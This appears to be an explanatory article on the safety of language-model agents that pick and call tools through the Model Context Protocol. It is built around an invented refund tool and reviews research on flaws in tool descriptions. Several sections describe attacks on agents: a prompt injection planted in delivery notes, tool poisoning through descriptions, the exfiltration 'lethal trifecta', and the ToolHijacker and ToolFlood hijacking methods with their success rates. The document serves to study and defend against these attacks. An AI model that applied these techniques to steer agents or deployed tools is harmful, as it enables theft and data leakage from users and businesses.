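# Safety of language-model agents that choose and call tools at runtime

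## How an agent finds and calls a tool at runtime

A language-model agent is a program in which a language model chooses actions and a second piece of software, the host, carries them out. The model only produces text. The host runs the model, gives it descriptions of the available tools, and executes or refuses the calls it writes. A tool is any function, web interface or command that the agent can call, such as a database query or a payment service. In ordinary software, a programmer reads a tool's documentation, writes code to call it, and relies on a compiler and tests to find mistakes before anyone uses the program. Many agents skip that stage and instead find a tool while they are working, read whatever description comes with it, and fill in the arguments on the spot.

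Agents often find and call tools through the Model Context Protocol (MCP), an open standard that the AI company Anthropic introduced in November 2024. It lets a host list and call the tools of a tool server, a program that offers tools and runs them on request. In its announcement of the latest version, the Model Context Protocol (2026) project reports close to half a billion monthly downloads of its main software development kits (SDKs), the libraries that developers use to build hosts and servers. Automated builds inflate download counts, so the figure is only a rough measure of how much MCP is used. Anthropic's *Bringing MCP 2026-07-28 to Claude* (2026) gives a firmer figure of over 950 servers in the directory for its Claude products.

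Suppose a user asks an agent for a 20-euro refund on an order. The agent finds a tool on the shop's tool server that it has never called before, `issue_refund(order_id: string, amount: integer)`. The tool's description gives no unit for the amount. The tool takes the amount in euros, but the agent sends 2000, meaning cents. The call is well formed, so no program reports an error, and the shop pays out 2,000 euros.

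### One call in five steps

The call passes through discovery, choice, assembly of the arguments, execution, and return of the result. Discovery takes one exchange of messages in JSON, a text format for structured data. The host sends a `tools/list` request:

```json
{
  "jsonrpc": "2.0", "id": 1, "method": "tools/list",
  "params": {
    "_meta": {
      "io.modelcontextprotocol/protocolVersion": "2026-07-28",
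      "io.modelcontextprotocol/clientCapabilities": {}
    }
  }
}
```

The server answers with its tools. For the invented refund tool, in the format that the specification sets out in Model Context Protocol's *Tools* (2026), the answer would be:

```json
{
  "jsonrpc": "2.0", "id": 1,
  "result": {
    "resultType": "complete",
    "tools": [{
      "name": "issue_refund",
      "description": "Issue a refund for an order",
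      "inputSchema": {
        "type": "object",
        "properties": {
          "order_id": { "type": "string" },
          "amount": { "type": "integer" }
        },
        "required": ["order_id", "amount"]
      }
    }],
    "ttlMs": 300000, "cacheScope": "public"
  }
}
```

The `inputSchema` is a machine-readable schema that states which fields and types a call may contain. The host puts the tool's name, description and schema into the text that the model reads. A server can also send a title and icons to display to the user, and annotations on the tool's behaviour, which the host must treat as untrusted unless it trusts the server. Some hosts withhold tools from the model at first. AI SDK's *dynamicTool*, a documentation page for a TypeScript library for building agents, describes a setting that keeps a tool out of the model's text until a search finds it.

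The model chooses a tool based on the user's request and the list of available tools, then writes the tool's name. MCP describes its tools as "model-controlled", meaning that the model can pick and call them without a programmer specifying when. The host then matches the name to a server. Tool names need only be unique within one server, so two servers may each offer a tool called `search`. The specification advises hosts to add a prefix to tell them apart, and warns against using the name a server gives itself as the prefix, because two servers can share that name too. Since the model uses the tools' descriptions to choose, a hostile server can try to steer the choice by putting instructions in them (tool poisoning).

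The model also assembles the arguments. It receives the schema, the description and the conversation so far, but not the tool's code. In the example, it takes the order number from the conversation and has to turn "20 euros" into an integer. The integer type is weak evidence for the wrong unit, cents, because programmers often store money as a whole number of cents to avoid rounding errors. The host can check the finished arguments against the schema, and some model providers exclude non-conforming text during generation (constrained decoding). Both methods allow the value 2000 because it is a valid integer.

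Execution starts when the host sends the call:

```json
{
  "jsonrpc": "2.0", "id": 2, "method": "tools/call",
  "params": {
    "name": "issue_refund",
    "arguments": { "order_id": "A-1043", "amount": 2000 },
    "_meta": {
      "io.modelcontextprotocol/protocolVersion": "2026-07-28",
      "io.modelcontextprotocol/clientCapabilities": {}
    }
  }
}
```

This is the last point at which the host can stop the payment. The Model Context Protocol specification recommends that hosts show the arguments to the user before sending them and ask for confirmation of sensitive operations. Both recommendations use the word "should", so a host that never asks can still implement the protocol. Servers, however, must validate all inputs, control access and limit the rate of calls. The model receives no information while the tool runs. If the server needs more input, such as a confirmation or a missing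 parameter, it can return a result of type `input_required`. The host then collects the answer and resends the original call with the answer attached. The call's side effect, the change it makes outside the agent, happens on the server's side.

The host receives the result and passes it to the model as text. There are two kinds of error. An unknown tool or a malformed request causes a protocol error, which the model is unlikely to be able to fix, according to the specification. A problem such as a wrongly formatted date or an out-of-range value causes a tool execution error, which the server marks with `isError: true`. The host should pass this second kind to the model so that the model can correct the call and retry. The refund call causes neither error. If the server replies "Refunded 2000 on order A-1043", the model still mistakes 2000 for cents, treats the reply as confirmation, and tells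 the user that 20 euros are on the way.

### What the July 2026 revision changed

The messages above follow the version of MCP released on 28 July 2026. It replaced the November 2025 version, and several of the changes affect what a host can check.

The largest change is the removal of sessions. Model Context Protocol's *Key Changes* (2026) records that, under the old version, host and server opened with a handshake, and over the web a session identifier could tie later requests to it. Now every request carries its own protocol version and the host's capabilities in the `_meta` field, and a server must reject a request that lacks either. The sample request in the release announcement lacks both, so a server that follows the specification would have to reject it. The more important consequence for safety is that a server must not vary its tool list from one connection to another or as a side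 effect of earlier requests on the same connection, though it may vary the list according to the caller's authorization. A server therefore breaks the protocol if it offers harmless tools at first and different ones after the first call on that connection. However, a server can ignore this rule, and even one that follows it may change its list over time.

When state has to last across calls, the model now copies identifiers from one call into the next. The host and the server also send their own names with each message, but Model Context Protocol's *Overview* (2026) tells implementers not to base security decisions on those names, since nobody verifies them.

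Tool lists now carry an expiry time. The `ttlMs` field in the answer above is 300,000 milliseconds, so the host may treat the list as fresh for five minutes after receiving it. The Model Context Protocol project said that under the May 2026 release candidate, hosts would know "exactly" how long a list stays fresh. In the final text, Model Context Protocol's *Caching* (2026) calls the value a hint and lets the server change its tools before the time runs out.

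Suppose the shop notices its omission and adds "amount in euros" to the description one minute after the agent fetched the list. The host can keep using the old text for four more minutes. A change notification would end that sooner, but only if the server offers them and the host has subscribed. If the shop had renamed the field, a call with the old name would probably have failed, and the specification allows a host to fetch the list again after such an error. But a change in the field's meaning causes no error if the name and type stay the same. This configuration is not rare, since the official Python SDK keeps lists by default whenever the server states a time, according to the Model Context Protocol documentation.

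The revision also widened what a schema can express. Previously, the top level of an input schema could hold only `type`, `properties` and `required`. *SEP-2106* (McBride and Hungerford, 2026), the proposal behind the change, opened it to the full vocabulary of JSON Schema 2020-12, the current edition of the usual schema language for JSON. A server can now require a caller to give either an ID or a name, but not both. The Agentic AI Foundation gives the example of a bank transfer schema that requires either a pair of internal accounts or an international account number with a bank code, and rejects calls that mix them. The richer vocabulary would not have prevented the refund error unless the shop had also set an upper limit, because 2000 is still a valid integer.

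*Measuring tool input schema fidelity*, by Hungerford, who also steered the proposal through, tested how much of the new vocabulary reaches the model. The study gave 24 models the schemas of six demonstration tools, with 20 trials for each pairing of model and schema. A trial succeeded if the arguments validated against the schema and respected the keyword under test. Some failures arose in the providers' interfaces, before the model was involved. Anthropic's interface and OpenAI's older one rejected the "exactly one of these" construction at the top level of a schema. The interface of Moonshot, a Chinese AI company, rejected a schema that the company's Kimi K3 model handled in every trial through another provider. Google's interface dropped the permitted values from some fields, so the models saw only the display labels.

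The test prompts made the task easier by supplying values that already fitted the schema. When Hungerford reran 22 of the models with more natural wording, 115 of 128 results stayed the same, though one small model, Gemma 4 31B, fell from 65% to 0% on the "exactly one" schema. Hungerford also found that neither the TypeScript nor the Python SDK validates such inputs faithfully unless the server's developer adds a validator. These are one person's results from one point in time, and the services change often, but they show that a constraint in a published schema may not reach the model, the server may not check it, or both.

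A richer schema language also adds a risk, because a JSON schema can use the keyword `$ref` to refer to another document by web address. As McBride and Hungerford point out, if a host fetches every such reference, a malicious tool definition can make it send requests from inside its network to internal addresses that an outsider could not reach. The final specification forbids automatic fetching from the network. Implementers may offer it as an option, off by default and preferably limited to a list of approved hosts. If a schema cannot be validated without the missing document, the host should reject it rather than assume that the missing part allows anything. The Model Context Protocol specification also recommends limits on schema depth and validation time, because a hostile schema can take enough computation to stall the validator.

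### How much is fixed beforehand

MCP is in the middle of a range that has typed stubs at one end. A typed stub is code, written or generated before deployment, that fixes a tool's name, parameters and types. If a programmer writes `issue_refund("A-1043", "twenty")` against a stub, the compiler rejects the line. When a model supplies the arguments, the host still has to check them at runtime, but against a schema that the developer chose and could test.

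When a tool's schema is fetched at runtime, the developer has written only a general routine that accepts any schema. In AI SDK, an ordinary tool's input has types known at compile time, such as a string for `location`, but a dynamic tool's input has the type `unknown`, so the developer has to validate or convert it at runtime. The library's example requires a field called `action` to be a string and allows any value in a field called `parameters`.

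When a tool has only prose documentation, the agent infers the field names and types from sentences and sample requests, and the host has no schema to validate the call against. A shell or code interpreter usually has a schema, but it contains a single string. Any program text fits that string, including a command that deletes a directory, so passing validation provides almost no information about what the call will do. If a tool has no documentation, the agent learns by sending calls and reading the errors. That is tolerable for a search function, but with `issue_refund`, every successful guess issues a real refund.

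A fetched schema lists fields and types, as a stub does, but the host's developer has never seen it. The server sends it during the run, and the same party may have written the schema, the description and the tool. Validation shows that the call matches what the server published, but nobody on the user's side has examined whether the tool does what the user wants.

Software engineers met a version of this problem in the 1990s with CORBA, a standard for calling objects on other machines. A CORBA program could make calls through static stubs, which a compiler generated from a description of the interface. It could also use the dynamic invocation interface to build a request at runtime from an object reference, an operation name and a list of parameters. According to Oracle's documentation, this interface could reach objects whose type was unknown when the programmer wrote the client. For these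 dynamic calls, the programmer's code "has to do the work of a client stub". Type checks moved from compilation to runtime, and the program could omit them. Micro Focus warned its customers that invalid arguments in a dynamic request could have unpredictable results, including server crashes.

CORBA's Interface Repository stored type information that programs could query while running. Schmidt and Vinoski (2003), in *Dynamic CORBA, Part 4*, credit it with helping to keep dynamic calls type-safe. A `tools/list` response does a similar job for an agent. Developers still used dynamic invocation less than stubs, according to Schmidt and Vinoski's *Dynamic CORBA, Part 1*, although the standard had included it since version 1.0 in 1991. A CORBA programmer wrote explicit code to turn type information into a request, whereas an agent leaves that step to a model's reading of a description. MCP has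 a counterpart to the repository's types but none to the programmer's understanding of what the operation was for, except to the extent that the model supplies it.

### Three ways for a call to go wrong

A type error is a call whose name, fields or values do not fit the interface. In the refund example, passing `amount: "20 euros"` or calling `issueRefund` would be a type error. A server that validates its inputs rejects such a call, so no money moves, and the agent may get to try again.

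An unintended action is a well-formed call whose effect the user did not want. Nobody means any harm in cases such as the 2,000-euro payment, a correct refund on the wrong order, or a second refund made because the agent did not detect that the first had gone through.

Misuse is the use of the agent's tools for harm, either by its user or by someone who manipulates the agent. A dishonest user might have it refund orders that were never returned. An outsider usually manipulates the model through prompt injection, which is text from an outside source that the model follows as if it were an instruction. For example, a customer could write in an order's delivery notes that the shop has approved a refund of every purchase since January. When the agent looks up the order, the host passes the notes to the model with the rest of the result, and the model starts issuing refunds. Tool descriptions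 can also contain injected instructions, which the model reads before it calls the tool.

The same call can fall under either of the last two headings or neither, and a schema check returns the same result in each case. For example, `issue_refund("A-1043", 2000)` is a mistake if the user wanted to refund 20 euros, theft if text in the delivery notes prompted it, and correct if the customer returned a 2,000-euro sofa.

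## What tool descriptions can state and whether they are true

The refund went wrong because the agent could not know that the tool took its amount in euros. JSON Schema can require an integer, or an integer below 500, but it has no keyword for a unit of measurement, so developers put units in prose. For example, the Model Context Protocol specification shows a weather tool that returns 22.5 in a field described as "Temperature in celsius" and another, on the same page, that returns 72°F. Only someone who reads the text can tell that the two temperatures are almost equal.

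A tool's prose description can also state facts that don't belong to any single field. For example, the specification advises a server that hands out temporary identifiers, such as one for a shopping basket, to state in the tool's description how long the identifiers last. The model reads that sentence and may act on it, but the host's software cannot check it.

### Inputs, outputs, preconditions and effects

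In the early 2000s, researchers working on "semantic web services" tried to put such facts in a form that software could reason about. Their best-known language was OWL-S, which its designers submitted to the World Wide Web Consortium (W3C), the web's main standards body, in 2004. An OWL-S description uses terms from an ontology, a formal vocabulary that defines concepts and how they relate. For example, an ontology might define a refund as a kind of payment. Each OWL-S description has three parts. The profile states what the service does, the process model sets out its steps, and the grounding maps both to the messages that a program sends.

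The profile lists inputs, outputs, preconditions and effects. Inputs and outputs are data. A precondition must be true before the call, and an effect is a change that the call makes in the world. OWL-S itself is written in long-winded XML, but in a simplified notation the refund tool could look like this:

```
service       issue_refund
input         order_id : OrderNumber
              amount   : MoneyAmount, unit = whole euros
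precondition  order_id is paid
              amount <= price paid - earlier refunds
output        receipt  : RefundReceipt
effect        the shop's balance falls by amount
              the customer's balance rises by amount
```

The unit is now part of the input's type. If the agent sent "2000 euro cents", software could detect the mismatch and convert the value to 20 euros. Software could not do this with a bare 2000, so the agent would have to label its values as carefully as the shop did. The precondition would also block a 2,000-euro refund on a 20-euro order, but only if a program checked it before the payment.

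People used such descriptions mainly to find services and to combine them. In *Semantic Matching of Web Services Capabilities*, Paolucci, Kawamura and colleagues (2002) built a matcher for the predecessor of OWL-S. It compared the outputs a requester wanted with those each service advertised. Exact matches ranked highest, followed by services that advertised a broader concept than the one requested, and then by those that advertised a narrower one. If neither concept included the other, the match failed. The requester and the service had to use terms from the ontology, but not the same terms, so a search for "card refund" could find a service that advertised "refund". The matcher also compared inputs, but not preconditions or effects.

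Researchers used planning programs to combine services. Given the goal "the customer has 20 euros back", a planner searches for a service with that effect and finds `issue_refund`. That service needs an order number, so the planner searches for a service that outputs one, such as an order search, and puts it first. Sirin, Parsia and colleagues (2004) adapted a planner called SHOP2 to do this with web services. While planning, it ran services that only gathered information and simulated those that changed the world. This was safe only if the descriptions correctly stated which kind each service was.

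Another group submitted the Web Service Modeling Ontology (WSMO) to the W3C in 2005. WSMO differs from OWL-S mainly in describing the requester's goal separately from the service and in making "mediators", components that resolve mismatches between the two, a basic part of the model. In the refund example, a mediator could convert cents to euros. WSMO also separates conditions on data from conditions on the world. A precondition concerns the input (the order number is well formed), while an assumption concerns the world (the customer has paid). Likewise, a postcondition concerns the output and an effect concerns the world.

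SAWSDL, a W3C standard since 2007, is much more modest. It adds three attributes to WSDL, the XML format developers already used to describe web services. One attribute links a part of the description to a concept in any ontology the developer chooses. The other two point to scripts that convert data between the service's format and the ontology's. The shop could link `amount` to a concept called "amount in euros" without rewriting anything else. SAWSDL was based on an earlier proposal that had fields for preconditions and effects, but the standard left them out.

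None of the three became common outside research. Pedrinaci and Domingue (2010), who worked in the field, examined why in *Toward the Next Wave of Services*. Companies had published few web services on the open web, so there was little to match or combine, and writing rich descriptions took a lot of skilled manual work. The benefits also depended on others making the same effort, because a matcher can compare two descriptions only if they share an ontology or someone has mapped one to the other.

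Language models remove much of that work. A model can read "amount in whole euros" without an ontology, and it can connect "give the customer their money back" to a tool called `issue_refund`. But models do not fix another weakness of OWL-S. The provider described the service's effects, and no part of the system checked that the service had those effects and no others.

### OpenAPI and MCP's four hints

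OpenAPI, the most widely used format for describing web interfaces, has no fields for preconditions or effects. An OpenAPI document lists the addresses that a program can call, the parameters and response schemas for each, how callers log in, and explanations in prose. Each operation's HTTP method does roughly indicate its effects, because the methods have standard meanings. GET should only read, and repeating a PUT or DELETE should have no further intended effect. POST guarantees neither, so a client should not automatically resend `POST /refunds`.

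MCP loses this information, since every call to a tool is the same `tools/call` message, whether it reads the weather or deletes a database. Its annotations restore some of it. They have been in the protocol since March 2025 and consist of a display title and four true-or-false hints. Model Context Protocol's *mcp_types*, the Python reference for the current version, gives these meanings and defaults:

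| Hint | Meaning if true | Default |
|---|---|---|
| `readOnlyHint` | The tool does not modify its environment | false |
| `destructiveHint` | The tool may make destructive changes, not just additions | true |
| `idempotentHint` | Repeating the call with the same arguments has no additional effect | false |
| `openWorldHint` | The tool may interact with an open set of outside entities, as a web search does | true |

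The second and third hints matter only for tools that are not read-only. A host could use the four hints to skip a confirmation, show a warning, retry after a failure, or examine a result for untrusted text.

Each hint defaults to the cautious value. A tool without annotations is treated as one that modifies things, perhaps destructively, is unsafe to repeat, and may bring in outside content. A server can therefore use the hints only to make its tool look safer than the default. This is helpful if the server's operator is honest, but a dishonest operator would want to send any hint that could change a host's behaviour. The protocol does not prevent a server from setting `readOnlyHint: true` on a tool that deletes files.

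MCP's designers knew this when they added the hints. Justin Spahr-Summers, one of the protocol's creators, asked how a host could use a flag it could not trust (Model Context Protocol, 2026). Another reviewer, Basil Hosmer, argued that hosts should ignore annotations from untrusted servers altogether. The specification calls every annotation a hint, which hosts distrust by default. The Python reference is stricter and says hosts should never base decisions about tool use on an untrusted server's annotations.

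Under the protocol, the host decides which servers to trust. A company that runs its own tool servers has good reasons to believe their hints. But according to Model Context Protocol, most hosts trust any server that the user has installed. Many servers send no annotations, and hosts differ in how strictly they apply the cautious defaults. As of March 2026, no host let users filter tools by annotation or showed the annotations in its approval prompts. The closest widely used feature was a read-only mode on GitHub's server, which about 17% of its users had switched on.

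Even accurate hints would do little to make the refund tool safer. The tool is not read-only, and it is not idempotent, because a second call pays the customer again. It is less clear whether the tool is destructive. A refund deletes nothing and adds an entry to the shop's accounts, so a careful developer could set `destructiveHint: false`. A host that warns only about destructive tools would then send a 2,000-euro payment without a warning. None of the four hints concerns money, and none could specify the unit of the refund amount.

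### Richer labels

Several proposals would extend this vocabulary. Model Context Protocol (MCP) listed five in March 2026, and the charter of its interest group on annotations lists six. The most developed, on trust and sensitivity, has co-authors from GitHub and OpenAI, who based it on gaps they found when running MCP in production. A second covers governance and the user interface. Three smaller ones would add one hint each: `unsafeOutputHint`, `secretHint` and `trustedHint`.

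A tool's risk depends on which other tools the agent has. The present hints handle this problem poorly, and much of the interest comes from it. Searching a user's emails is harmless on its own but becomes dangerous if the agent also reads text from strangers and can send data out, because a stranger can then instruct the model to find private emails and send them. The programmer Simon Willison calls this combination the "lethal trifecta". One reader of his newsletter suggested labelling each tool by whether it reads private data, exposes the agent to untrusted content or can send data out, and having the host block any session that combines all three. The host could do this without understanding the tools, but only if every tool were labelled correctly.

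At least one commercial product already uses typed effect labels. StackOne, whose connectors link agents to other companies' software, lets developers label each action with effects such as `read`, `write`, `delete` or `execute`, and derives the MCP hints from those labels. It marks an action as destructive if any of its effects is `delete`, though developers can override the result by hand. One label is easier to get right than four separate hints, and it cannot produce contradictory hints by accident. But creating a support ticket counts as `write`, and therefore as non-destructive, and a refund presumably would too. A "moves money" label would be more useful to the shop than any of these.

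A shop can state the unit of a payment amount without waiting for a new standard. MCP tools have a `_meta` field that accepts custom entries, so the shop could publish `com.example/amount-unit: "EUR"` today, and its own host could check that entry before every payment. Other companies' hosts would ignore the entry because they are not built to recognize it, which is a smaller version of the old problem of agreeing on a shared ontology.

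The Model Context Protocol project distinguishes hints from contracts, and the distinction applies to all these proposals. Even if some servers get a hint wrong, it can still be useful, for example by helping a host choose what to show the user. If safety depends on the label being true, the project says that access controls, the network or the runtime should provide the guarantee.

### Comparing descriptions with code

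How often descriptions are wrong in practice is an empirical question, and researchers can study it for tools whose source code is public. The most careful attempt so far is by Shi, Zhang and colleagues (2026), in *Description-Code Inconsistency in Real-world MCP Servers*. They treat everything that the model sees (name, schema and description) as a claim about the tool's functionality F and its effects E on the environment. A tool is inconsistent if

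```
F_claimed ≠ F_actual    or    E_actual ⊈ E_claimed
```

A description has to match the tool's functionality exactly. It also has to include every effect the tool has, but it may include effects that never happen. The definition yields seven categories, shown here with invented versions of the refund tool. The first four concern functionality, and the last three concern undeclared side effects.

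| Category | Description | What the code does |
|---|---|---|
| Undeclared functionality | "Issue a refund" | Issues the refund and orders a replacement |
| Overclaimed functionality | "Refund to a card or bank account" | Refunds to cards only |
| Misclaimed functionality | "Look up a refund" | Issues a refund |
| Ambiguous functionality | "Process an order" | Issues a refund |
| Resource overconsumption | "Issue a refund" | Downloads the shop's whole order history first |
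| State mutation | "Issue a refund" | Also locks the customer's account |
| Data leakage | "Issue a refund" | Also sends the customer's details to an advertiser |

Shi and colleagues built a program called DCIChecker to find such cases. It first reads a server's source code, without running it, to find each tool and its description. It then gathers the tool's main function, the project's own functions that the main function calls (up to three levels deep), and any sensitive operations such as network requests or file deletions. Finally, a language model, Claude Sonnet 4.5, compares the description with the gathered code.

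The second stage prompts the model twice, because the wording of the question affects the answer. One prompt asks whether the description and code are consistent, the other whether they are inconsistent. If the answers differ, even just in the category, a third prompt gives the model both lines of reasoning and asks for a verdict. On a sample of 400 real tools, the first prompt alone found 47% of the inconsistent ones. The second found all of them, but 21% of its alarms were false. The full procedure found 97%, with 4% false alarms, and classified 96.75% of the tools correctly. It needed the third prompt for 38% of the tools.

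The 97% figure overstates DCIChecker's detection rate. Human reviewers checked 200 tools that the program had called inconsistent and 200 that it had called consistent, and found 8 errors in the first group and 5 in the second. But in the full data, the program called about eight times as many tools consistent as inconsistent, so the equal-sized groups understate the share of inconsistent tools it missed. If the sample's error rates hold for the full data, it correctly found around 1,830 inconsistent tools and missed around 380, which is a detection rate of about 83%. This estimate is rough because it is based on only five misses.

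The same sample also makes rival programs look worse than they are. DCIChecker had already flagged 192 of its 197 inconsistent tools, so a rival could have found at most five more. A fairer comparison uses 280 inconsistent pairs that the team made by altering correct ones, with 40 in each category. DCIChecker found 263 of them. The next best program, a reimplementation of an earlier method for comparing descriptions with code, found 112, and general security scanners found between 8 and 69. DCIChecker did worst on ambiguous descriptions, finding 26 of 40. The original refund tool could probably fall only into this category, since its code does issue a refund, as described, so DCIChecker might well fail to flag the missing unit.

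Shi and colleagues ran DCIChecker on 19,200 tools from 2,214 public servers written in Python. It flagged 1,907 tools as inconsistent, or 11.2% of those with a description it could compare. These tools appeared on 775 servers, or 35%. The true share of inconsistent tools is probably somewhat higher, since the program seems to miss more of them than it wrongly flags. The 8% of servers with three or more inconsistent tools accounted for 60% of the cases. Another 2,170 tools had no description. The team suspects that some developers did not know that the Python SDK takes the description from a comment in the code and sends none if the comment is missing.

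Many of the mismatches are documentation errors that pose no threat. Overclaimed functionality was the largest category, at 35.4% of cases, and it typically leads an agent to pick a tool that cannot do the job. Undeclared side effects made up 24.8%, or about 470 tools. These are more worrying because a tool can complete the task while also doing something that its description doesn't disclose to the model or the user. The study counted each tool only under its main category, so tools in other categories may also have undeclared side effects.

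The cases vary in seriousness. One tool was described as providing local weather forecasts but looked up exchange rates, which an agent would notice quickly. A tool for converting PDF files "locally" uploaded them to an outside service. An echo tool, which should only repeat a message, added a secret key from the server's settings to its reply. The case closest to the refund was a tool for placing orders on a financial exchange. According to its description, the user had to approve each order before execution, but the code submitted the order immediately. The developer may have been counting on the host to ask for approval, which MCP recommends but does not require. An agent that believed the description would have had no reason to ask the user.

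### Common faults and their effect on the model's choice

An earlier study covers more servers but with weaker evidence. Wang, Li and colleagues (2026), in *From Docs to Descriptions*, collected 10,831 servers in several programming languages in March 2025. They borrowed quality criteria from software documentation, such as accuracy and completeness, and had a small language model, GPT-4o-mini, compare each description with its code and sort the problems into categories. The result was 18 kinds of fault in four groups:

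| Group | Faults and number of cases |
|---|---|
| Accuracy | Wrong parameter meaning (3,449), unclear boundaries (1,137), undeclared behaviour (931), non-existent behaviour (572), wrong parameter type (203), inconsistent behaviour (72) |
| Functionality | Repeated tool name (7,894), confusing description of the function (3,572), no statement of when to use the tool (2,972), confusing statement of when to use it (1,583) |
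| Completeness | No description of return values (3,093), no description of a parameter (1,285), missing side effects (773), no parameter type (14) |
| Conciseness | Irrelevant details (2,904), overuse of technical terms (467), useless qualifiers (324), repetition (154) |

Repeated tool names, such as `read_file`, are the most frequent fault and the least serious. Wang and colleagues report them in 73% of servers, but a host can tell the tools apart by adding prefixes. Wrong parameter meanings are more serious because they lead to calls that pass every type check but do the wrong thing. The shop's description would have this fault if it said "amount in cents" for a tool that takes euros. The actual refund tool doesn't explain `amount` at all, so it would count under missing parameter descriptions.

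These counts are less reliable than those of Shi and colleagues. Wang and colleagues' paper gives no error rate for GPT-4o-mini's labels, and it sometimes describes the counts as servers and sometimes as tools, so they are hard to convert to percentages. Wang and colleagues found more tools that did something undeclared than tools that lacked a claimed function, while Shi and colleagues found that overclaiming was the most common mismatch. The studies used different samples, dates and definitions, which may account for most of the disagreement.

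The second half of the study tests whether these faults affect which tool a model chooses. For ten types of server, the team kept the code fixed and wrote descriptions that did well or badly in one of the four groups. It replaced the tools' names with random identifiers so the model could not choose by name. GPT-4o-mini then received 100 requests per server, each in a new session. The requests ranged from "Read file." to detailed instructions with a full file path.

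| Group | Chosen when done well | Chosen when done badly | Difference (percentage points) |
|---|---|---|---|
| Functionality | 17.8% | 6.2% | 11.6 |
| Accuracy | 15.9% | 7.1% | 8.8 |
| Completeness | 14.3% | 8.4% | 5.9 |
| Conciseness | 10.6% | 9.1% | 1.5 |

The eight rates add up to 89%, which suggests that the versions competed for the same requests, although the paper does not say so. A clear statement of the tool's purpose helped most when the request was short, a difference of 14.2 points. With detailed requests, functionality and accuracy had about equal effects, and complete descriptions became more important.

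A second experiment used real servers. In each of ten fields, such as calendars and databases, Wang and colleagues took five servers that did the same job and rewrote the description of one. The model chose the rewritten server 72% of the time, compared with the 20% expected by chance. The share ranged from 65% for location services to 81% for file systems. However, the 20% baseline is an assumption, because the paper reports no test of the same servers with their original descriptions. If the model already preferred some of the chosen servers, the rewriting had a smaller effect than the difference between 20% and 72%. Both experiments used a single small model that is now old, so newer models may respond differently.

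The experiments show that wording alone can move a large share of a model's choices from one server to another. They do not quite support the paper's conclusion that faulty descriptions cause "measurable selection failures", because the competing tools did the same thing and any choice would have completed the task.

In the accuracy result, the model could not have known which descriptions were accurate, because it never saw the code. It must have preferred something in the text, perhaps precise statements about parameters and limits. An equally precise but false description would probably have done just as well, and a server's owner can write one on purpose. Good descriptions therefore help honest developers gain users, but users cannot treat them as evidence of honesty.

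### What a comparison cannot establish

Both studies compared descriptions with code without running the tools. This can show that a description contradicts the code, but a match is much weaker evidence that the tool will do what its description states. Many tools do little more than pass requests to another service. Of the 7,562 sensitive operations that Shi and colleagues found, nearly half were network calls. DCIChecker can detect that a tool sends data to an address, but not what the program at that address does with it. It also does not follow calls into outside libraries, where a hostile developer could hide harmful code.

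The refund tool's code might do little more than send `amount` to the shop's payment processor. A reviewer could not tell from that code whether the processor expects euros or cents. They would need to check the processor's documentation and trust that it is correct.

The host usually cannot compare a remote tool's description with its code. MCP does not require a server to publish its source, and the host sees only the tool list and the results of calls. If a server publishes an output schema, it must return structured results that fit it, but the schema constrains only the form of the results. For example, a server could return a valid receipt and also sell the customer's address. Even if the source is public, the host cannot tell whether the server is running that version. The operator can replace the program between two calls without changing the tool's name, schema or description.

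Test calls reveal some of what a comparison misses. The shop could have refunded one euro on a dummy order and checked the account. This would have exposed the wrong unit, but it would have required a real payment. A test also covers only the inputs tried and the effects observable from outside. Test results also become outdated. If the payment processor switched from euros to cents the next day, the tool's code and description would still match, but a refund of 20 euros would pay the customer 20 cents.

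## How an agent chooses a tool and how a hostile description changes the choice

A host with a handful of tools can put every description into the text that the model reads. With thousands of tools, the descriptions would not fit or would leave little room for the task, so the host first searches the catalogue and shows the model only the best matches. The search is called retrieval, and the model's choice among the matches is called selection.

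For retrieval, the host uses an embedding model, which turns a text into a vector (a list of numbers). Texts with similar meanings tend to get vectors that point in similar directions. The host computes one vector q for the user's request and one vector t for each tool's name and description, then compares them, usually by cosine similarity:

```
sim(q, t) = (q · t) / (|q| |t|)
```

A score of 1 means the vectors point in the same direction, and 0 means they are perpendicular. The host keeps the k tools with the highest scores. The model then reads their descriptions and picks a tool or none.

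Suppose the user writes, "The lamp in order A-1043 arrived broken. Give the customer 20 euros back." To keep the arithmetic simple, this example represents the request as the vector (2, 2, 1), using three invented dimensions for payment, damage and delivery. Real vectors have hundreds or thousands of dimensions that nobody can label.

| Tool | Description | Vector | Score |
|---|---|---|---|
| `send_voucher` | "Compensate a customer whose order arrived broken or late" | (1, 2, 2) | 0.89 |
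| `report_damage` | "Report goods that arrived broken" | (0, 2, 1) | 0.75 |
| `issue_refund` | "Issue a refund for an order" | (3, 0, 0) | 0.67 |
| `track_parcel` | "Find a late or damaged parcel" | (0, 1, 2) | 0.60 |

The voucher tool's score is (2×1 + 2×2 + 1×2) / (3×3), or 0.89. If k is 2, the model receives only the voucher and damage tools. It cannot choose `issue_refund`, however capable it is, and will probably send a voucher to a customer who was owed money. Nobody attacked the agent, and every description is true. The refund tool ranked third because its description mentions only refunds, while the request was largely about a broken lamp. Setting k to 3 would include it, but would also give the model more text to process and more wrong tools to choose from.

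Ordinary search models often fail to find the right tool. *Retrieval Models Aren't Tool-Savvy* (2025) tested them on 7,600 tasks and 43,000 tools, and attributed their weak results partly to requests sharing few words with the descriptions of the right tools. Agents can also make errors when choosing among the tools they are offered. When *BiasBusters* (2025) offered models several tools that did the same job, some models favoured particular tools and others favoured particular positions in the list. In *Tool Preferences in Agentic LLMs are Unreliable* (2025), editing only a tool's description made GPT-4.1 and a small Qwen model use that tool up to ten times as often.

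### Getting a hostile tool chosen

An attacker who publishes a tool in an open catalogue has to get it through both retrieval and selection. *Prompt Injection Attack to Tool Selection in LLM Agents* (Shi, Yuan and colleagues, 2025) presents ToolHijacker, an attack that uses a separate part of the tool's description for each step. One part matches the requests users are likely to make, and the other persuades the model to prefer the tool. The attacker needs no access to the victim's catalogue or models and instead tunes the text on a substitute catalogue and models.

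The team added one such tool to a library of 9,650 and tried seven tasks, each worded 100 ways. In the version of the attack that did not need a model's gradients, the hostile tool reached the top five in 95% of cases, and GPT-4o chose it in 85%. Without the attack, GPT-4o chose a suitable tool 98% of the time. A smaller test on one task tried the two parts of the attack separately. With only the matching part, the host always retrieved the tool, but the model chose it just 5% of the time. With only the persuasive part, those rates were 65% and 63%. The eight models in the study are now old, and newer ones may be less susceptible.

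Persuasion matters less if the attacker can fill every place in the results. In *ToolFlood*, Jawad and Brunel (2026) tested this on a catalogue of 11,759 tools with k set to 5. For each of ten tasks, they used 100 sample requests to write the hostile descriptions and 50 others to test them. An average of 145 added tools per task, about 1.2% of the catalogue, took all five places for 91% of the test requests. Depending on the model, the agent chose a hostile tool for 95% to 96% of requests. Each set of added tools targeted only one task, however, and an attacker who wanted to capture many unrelated tasks would need many more.

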